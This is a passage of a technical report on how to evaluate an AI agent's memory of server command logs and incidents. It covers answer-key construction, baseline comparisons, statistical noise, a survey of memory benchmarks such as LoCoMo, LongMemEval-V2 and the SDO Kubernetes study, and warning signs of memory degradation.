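Recall@k measures the share of a question's relevant records that appear in the top k results, so each test question needs a complete list of those records. For questions about events and lists, an exact database query on host, user and time can usually produce that list. The query has to account for complications such as commands run through `sudo`.

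No exact query finds every note about similar symptoms, so to build the answer key for such questions, the engineers can run several kinds of search, combine the results and have a person judge each item. *LongMemEval-V2* (Wu, Ji and colleagues, 2026), a benchmark of web agents, used a coding agent to propose the relevant records and people to check them. A record that every search missed will still be absent from the answer key, so measured recall will be slightly too high.

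The store must also contain plausible wrong answers. For the restart of web-03, these are records of the same command on other hosts and on other days. The full log includes 3,600 such restarts, but a random sample of one line in 1,000 would include only three or four, which would make the test far too easy. Engineers who can't index the whole log for a test should deliberately add near-duplicates to the sample.

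Finally, the test questions should come from a later period than the data used for tuning. The engineers could choose their settings with questions from September and October, then run the test once on questions from November. For each question, the store should hold only records from before the question arose. Otherwise the agent could find the note it wrote after solving the incident.

Recurring faults will appear on both sides of the split, as they do in practice, so the test should report results for familiar and new faults separately. In *A Self-Defining Operator for Distributed Applications*, Li, Anderson and colleagues (2026) built a memory from 50 incidents, froze it, and tested it on 30 incidents with familiar causes and 30 with new ones.

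### What to compare and measure

The engineers should run the same questions on six versions of the system, with the same model and tools:

| Version | What its score shows |
|---|---|
| No memory | What the agent can work out from general knowledge and the live machines |
| Latest records only | Whether recent history is enough |
| Word matching | What a cheap index achieves |
| Vector search | What embeddings achieve on their own |
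| Full system | Whether the extra parts are worth their cost |
| Right items placed by hand | What this model could achieve with perfect storage and search |

Suppose the agent answers 20 per cent of the questions correctly without memory, 62 per cent with the full system and 90 per cent when the right items are supplied by hand. The memory has then achieved 42 points of a possible 70-point gain, or 60 per cent. Better storage and search could add up to 28 more points, but gaining the last 10 would require a better model or prompt.

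These versions also expose bad questions. For example, a question that the agent can answer without any memory doesn't measure the memory. *DolphinBench* keeps a test only if an agent passes it with the relevant history and fails it without that history.

For each version, the engineers should record four things:

- **Recall@k**, for the number of results the program actually puts in the prompt. If the agent changed twelve servers and the first ten results cover eight of them, recall@10 is 67 per cent, out of a possible 83.
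- **The final result.** For a task, a program should check the state of the machine, as MERIT does with its database.
- **Cost**, including the model calls that write and maintain the store.
- **Delay**, including any time the agent spends rewording its queries. The slowest tenth of the searches matters as well as the median, since the site may be down while the agent waits.

### How many questions are enough

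If the full system answers 80 of 100 questions correctly, its true success rate could be several points higher or lower:

```
standard error:  √(0.80 × 0.20 / 100) = 0.04
95% interval:    0.80 ± 1.96 × 0.04 ≈ 0.72 to 0.88
```

Intervals calculated this way contain the true rate about 95 per cent of the time. Halving the width takes four times as many questions, so a score of 80 per cent on 400 questions gives a range of 76 to 84. The formula assumes that the questions are independent. The engineers learn less from a hundred questions about ten incidents than from a hundred independent questions, because one missing note could cause ten wrong answers.

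When two versions answer the same questions, only the questions that one gets right and the other gets wrong help show which is better. Suppose only the full system is right on 12 of the 100 questions, and only word matching is right on 5. The full system leads by seven points, but if the two were equally good, a split at least this uneven would still occur about one time in seven. With 400 questions and a split of 48 to 20, the lead would still be seven points, but a split at least that uneven would occur only about one time in 1,000.

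Published comparisons of memory systems often ignore noise. Penfield estimates in *Proposal* that, when systems are compared on a single category of LoCoMo questions, 56 per cent of the differences can't be distinguished from noise.

### Benchmarks of conversation

LoCoMo and LongMemEval, which supplied many of the results in earlier sections, test memory of chats. LoCoMo's ten conversations average 27 sessions and about 16,600 tokens, according to *AMA* (2026). It has 1,986 questions, but Li and colleagues, who built LYCHEEMEMORY V2, followed the usual practice of leaving out the adversarial ones and scoring the other 1,540.

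The original *LongMemEval* (Wu, Wang and colleagues, 2024) contains 500 questions about a user's chats with an assistant. They test whether a system can find a detail, combine information from several sessions, reason about dates, notice changed facts and decline to answer when the history lacks the information. Each question comes with about 115,000 tokens of history in the short version and 1.5 million in the long one. People marked where the evidence is, so the benchmark can measure recall@k as well as answer accuracy. GPT-4o answered 87.0 per cent of questions correctly when it received only the relevant sessions, and 60.6 per cent when it had to read the whole short history.

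Both benchmarks now leave little room for improvement. Mem0's *ai memory benchmarks in 2026* reports the company's own scores of 92.5 per cent on LoCoMo and 94.4 per cent on LongMemEval. *We audited LoCoMo*, by penfieldlabs, found errors in 99 of the 1,540 LoCoMo answers, so a perfect system would score only about 94 per cent under strict marking. However, the language model that judged the answers accepted up to 63 per cent of deliberately wrong ones. The audit also notes that the short LongMemEval history fits into a current context window. A two-point lead on either benchmark is therefore a poor reason to choose a memory system for servers.

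### Benchmarks of an agent's own work

LongMemEval-V2, from May 2026, is closer to the fleet's needs. Its 451 questions are about recorded runs in which agents used a shop, its administration pages, a forum and ServiceNow, a system that companies use for IT requests. The questions cover what a page contains, how actions change it, how to complete common tasks, which traps recur, and which assumptions are false on these sites. The memory receives either 100 runs (25 million tokens) or about 500 (115 million). It returns up to 200,000 tokens of evidence to a fixed model, Qwen3.5-9B, which writes the answer.

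| Memory | Correct, 100 runs | Correct, 500 runs | Delay per question, 500 runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 1% | 1% | none |
| Vector search over pages | 43% | 38% | 0.1 s |
| Vector search over pages and notes | 51% | 46% | 0.3 s |
| AgentRunbook-R | 59% | 57% | 26 s |
| Codex searching files | 70% | 69% | 186 s |
| AgentRunbook-C | 75% | 70% | 140 s |

Wu and colleagues built both AgentRunbook systems. AgentRunbook-R has a model write separate vector searches for pages, changes between pages, and notes. AgentRunbook-C has the coding agent Codex search files, and gives it instructions, an overview of the stored runs and a script for inspecting them. Searching files gave better answers than vector search but took minutes instead of seconds. The model may account for part of that lead, because GPT-5.4 mini controlled the file searches and the smaller Qwen3.5-9B controlled AgentRunbook-R.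 With 500 runs, AgentRunbook-C's lead over plain Codex was about six questions, which could be due to chance.

When the researchers placed the right page excerpts and notes in the prompt by hand, Qwen3.5-9B correctly answered 82.5 per cent of the questions that had no false premise. It answered only 48 per cent of those about recurring traps, so better search alone would not solve them. Many questions could be answered only from failed runs, which is a reason for the server agent to save its unsuccessful repairs too. The benchmark covers only browser work, and its records resemble the fleet's tickets more than the fleet's command log.

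In June 2026, Zhou, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Are We Ready For An Agent-Native Memory System?*, published a comparison across 11 datasets. They tested 12 memory systems, along with plain vector search and a model that read the history directly. No system led everywhere:

- On LongMemEval, Zep did best, with 48.0 per cent of its answers judged correct.
- On LoCoMo, MemOS had the most answers that matched the key exactly, at 11.5 per cent. This measure rejects correct answers in different words, which helps explain the low figure.
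- On DB-Bench, a set of database tasks from *LifelongAgentBench* (2025), MemoChat completed the most tasks, at 55.4 per cent.

Even the ranking of search methods depended on the cut-off. SimpleMem had the highest recall@1 on LoCoMo, 39.0 per cent, but A-Mem was well ahead at larger cut-offs, with a recall@10 of 85.9 per cent. For plain vector search, the score for overlap with the correct answer also fell from 37.1 to 7.4 as the evidence moved further back in the conversation. A test for the fleet therefore needs questions about older records, such as those from August, as well as last week's.

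On LongMemEval's questions about changed facts, Zep's answers contained the correct text 44.4 per cent of the time, compared with 20.0 per cent for plain vector search and 15.6 per cent for Mem0. Zep was much slower than LightMem, taking 155 seconds per question, including each question's share of the time spent building the memory, compared with 3.7 seconds. On a combined quality scale of 0 to 100, Zep scored above 84 and LightMem scored 48.

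### No public benchmark for command logs

As of December 2026, there appears to be no public benchmark that tests an agent's memory of command logs and host records across sessions. ExCyTIn-Bench has agents search security logs, but it doesn't test what they retain from one investigation to the next. MERIT includes IT operations, but with at most six sessions and a few important facts. Others cover related work:

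- *LifelongAgentBench* includes operating-system tasks and gives the agent up to 16 of its earlier successful runs.
- *Who Remembers What?* (2026) tests what agents carry over between tasks, some of them on the command line.
- *DreamBench-SWE* (2026) follows programming agents over several sessions and scores whether their memory returns current items and suppresses stale ones.
- *Incident Memory* (2026) derives 39 repair procedures from a history of IT service tickets. They covered 84.3 per cent of the incidents held back for testing.
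- Goel, Lavoie and colleagues (2026), in *HEAMS*, combine ten benchmarks that also cover privacy, deletion and planted false memories, but all ten use chats.

The closest experiment is Li, Anderson and colleagues' study of agents that repair applications on Kubernetes, a system for running software across many machines. Their own system, SDO, writes two things after each repair. A playbook describes how to confirm and fix the fault, and a detector is a small program that checks for the fault's symptoms and returns the playbook. They ran the same sequence of 200 incidents with four kinds of memory, using Claude Sonnet 4.6 each time:

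| Memory | Incidents diagnosed and repaired |
|---|---|
| None | 62.7% |
| Past investigations, found by vector search | 59.4% |
| Past investigations, chosen by the model from summaries | 31.8% |
| SDO | 65.4% |

With 200 incidents, each figure is uncertain by about seven points, so the study doesn't establish that SDO solved more incidents than an agent without memory. The drop to 31.8 per cent is far too large to be due to chance. Li and colleagues found that the agent kept following the explanation from an early match even when later evidence contradicted it. Without a no-memory version for comparison, the test would not have revealed that this memory did harm.

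SDO's clearest benefit was speed. On the 30 incidents with familiar causes, the median time to a repair fell from 584 to 282 seconds. SDO solved 18 of these incidents and the agent without memory solved 19, so a test that measured only success would have found no benefit.

The researchers also compared three ways of finding the right playbooks in the same collection:

| Search | Precision | Recall | Median time | Median tokens |
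|---|---|---|---|---|
| Vector search | 8% | 40% | 64 s | 62,000 |
| Model chooses from the playbooks | 53% | 77% | 483 s | 148,000 |
| Detectors | 48% | 73% | 11 s | 0 |

The vector search always returned five playbooks, which lowers its precision, and it used an embedding model from 2023. It also had to match specific symptoms to deliberately general instructions. The detectors avoided that mismatch by checking the machines' state directly. The experiment doesn't answer the main question about command logs. The memory held the agent's own investigations and repairs, so the test doesn't show whether an agent could find a command that an engineer ran three weeks earlier.

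There is no common benchmark for memory over command logs, so a company that sells one has no public score to support its claims, and a high score on LongMemEval is no substitute. Buyers should ask for a trial on their own records that compares the product with no memory and with word matching. The claim that embeddings don't work on logs also needs caution, because experiments have measured parts of the problem, such as near-identical code, numbers and private identifiers, but not how much each part harms an agent that works on real servers for months.

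### Signs that the memory has degraded

A memory system that passes a test can fail it later. Zhu and colleagues tracked ten memory systems over 50 simulated sessions. Plain vector search kept every fact, and they measured it on facts that never changed. Its accuracy still fell by 0.29 to 0.37 on a scale from 0 to 1, depending on the model, between the eighth and the last session, because similar items crowded out the right ones. With GPT-4o mini, the agent rarely declined to answer and increasingly gave a value that belonged to someone else. The prompt discouraged it from declining, but the result still suggests that it is risky to wait for the agent to report that it can't find something.

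Replacing a model can cause a sudden loss. In the worst case that Zhu and colleagues measured, a memory that a model regularly rewrote lost 64 percentage points more of its stored facts after a change of model than it did in a run without the change. Stores that kept the original text lost none. The engineers should therefore rerun the test set after every change of model, parser or index. Between tests, they can watch four signs in the agent's own logs:

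| Sign | Possible fault in the memory | Harmless explanation |
|---|---|---|
| The agent repeats actions that failed before | It didn't store the failure, or the search misses it | It is retrying after a temporary fault |
| More searches return nothing | A log has a gap, or a field has a new name | More questions concern quiet machines |
| Live checks contradict stored facts | Nobody updates the items after changes | Engineers have just rebuilt several servers |
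| Old items dominate the results | New items aren't reaching the index, or stale ones lack replacement links | The best match really is old |

A program can count repeated failures by comparing each failed command with earlier failures on the same host and software version. If repeats rise from one failed command in 50 in September to one in 12 in November, the engineers should check whether the earlier failures are in the store and whether a search finds them.

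Empty results are a useful signal only for searches that can return nothing, such as database queries and word matching. Vector search always returns something unless the program sets a minimum similarity, so the engineers can instead count how often the agent rewords a query or answers "not found".

The age of the results should be compared with the age of the whole store, because a growing store gets older on average. If the fleet's log has grown evenly for 90 days, half its lines are more than 45 days old, so results with a median age of 70 days would deserve a closer look, especially for questions about the current state of a machine. The engineers should find the cause before deleting anything. Li, Anderson and colleagues' system never removes a playbook for lack of use, because a repair needed once a year is the one an agent is least likely to work out again from scratch.
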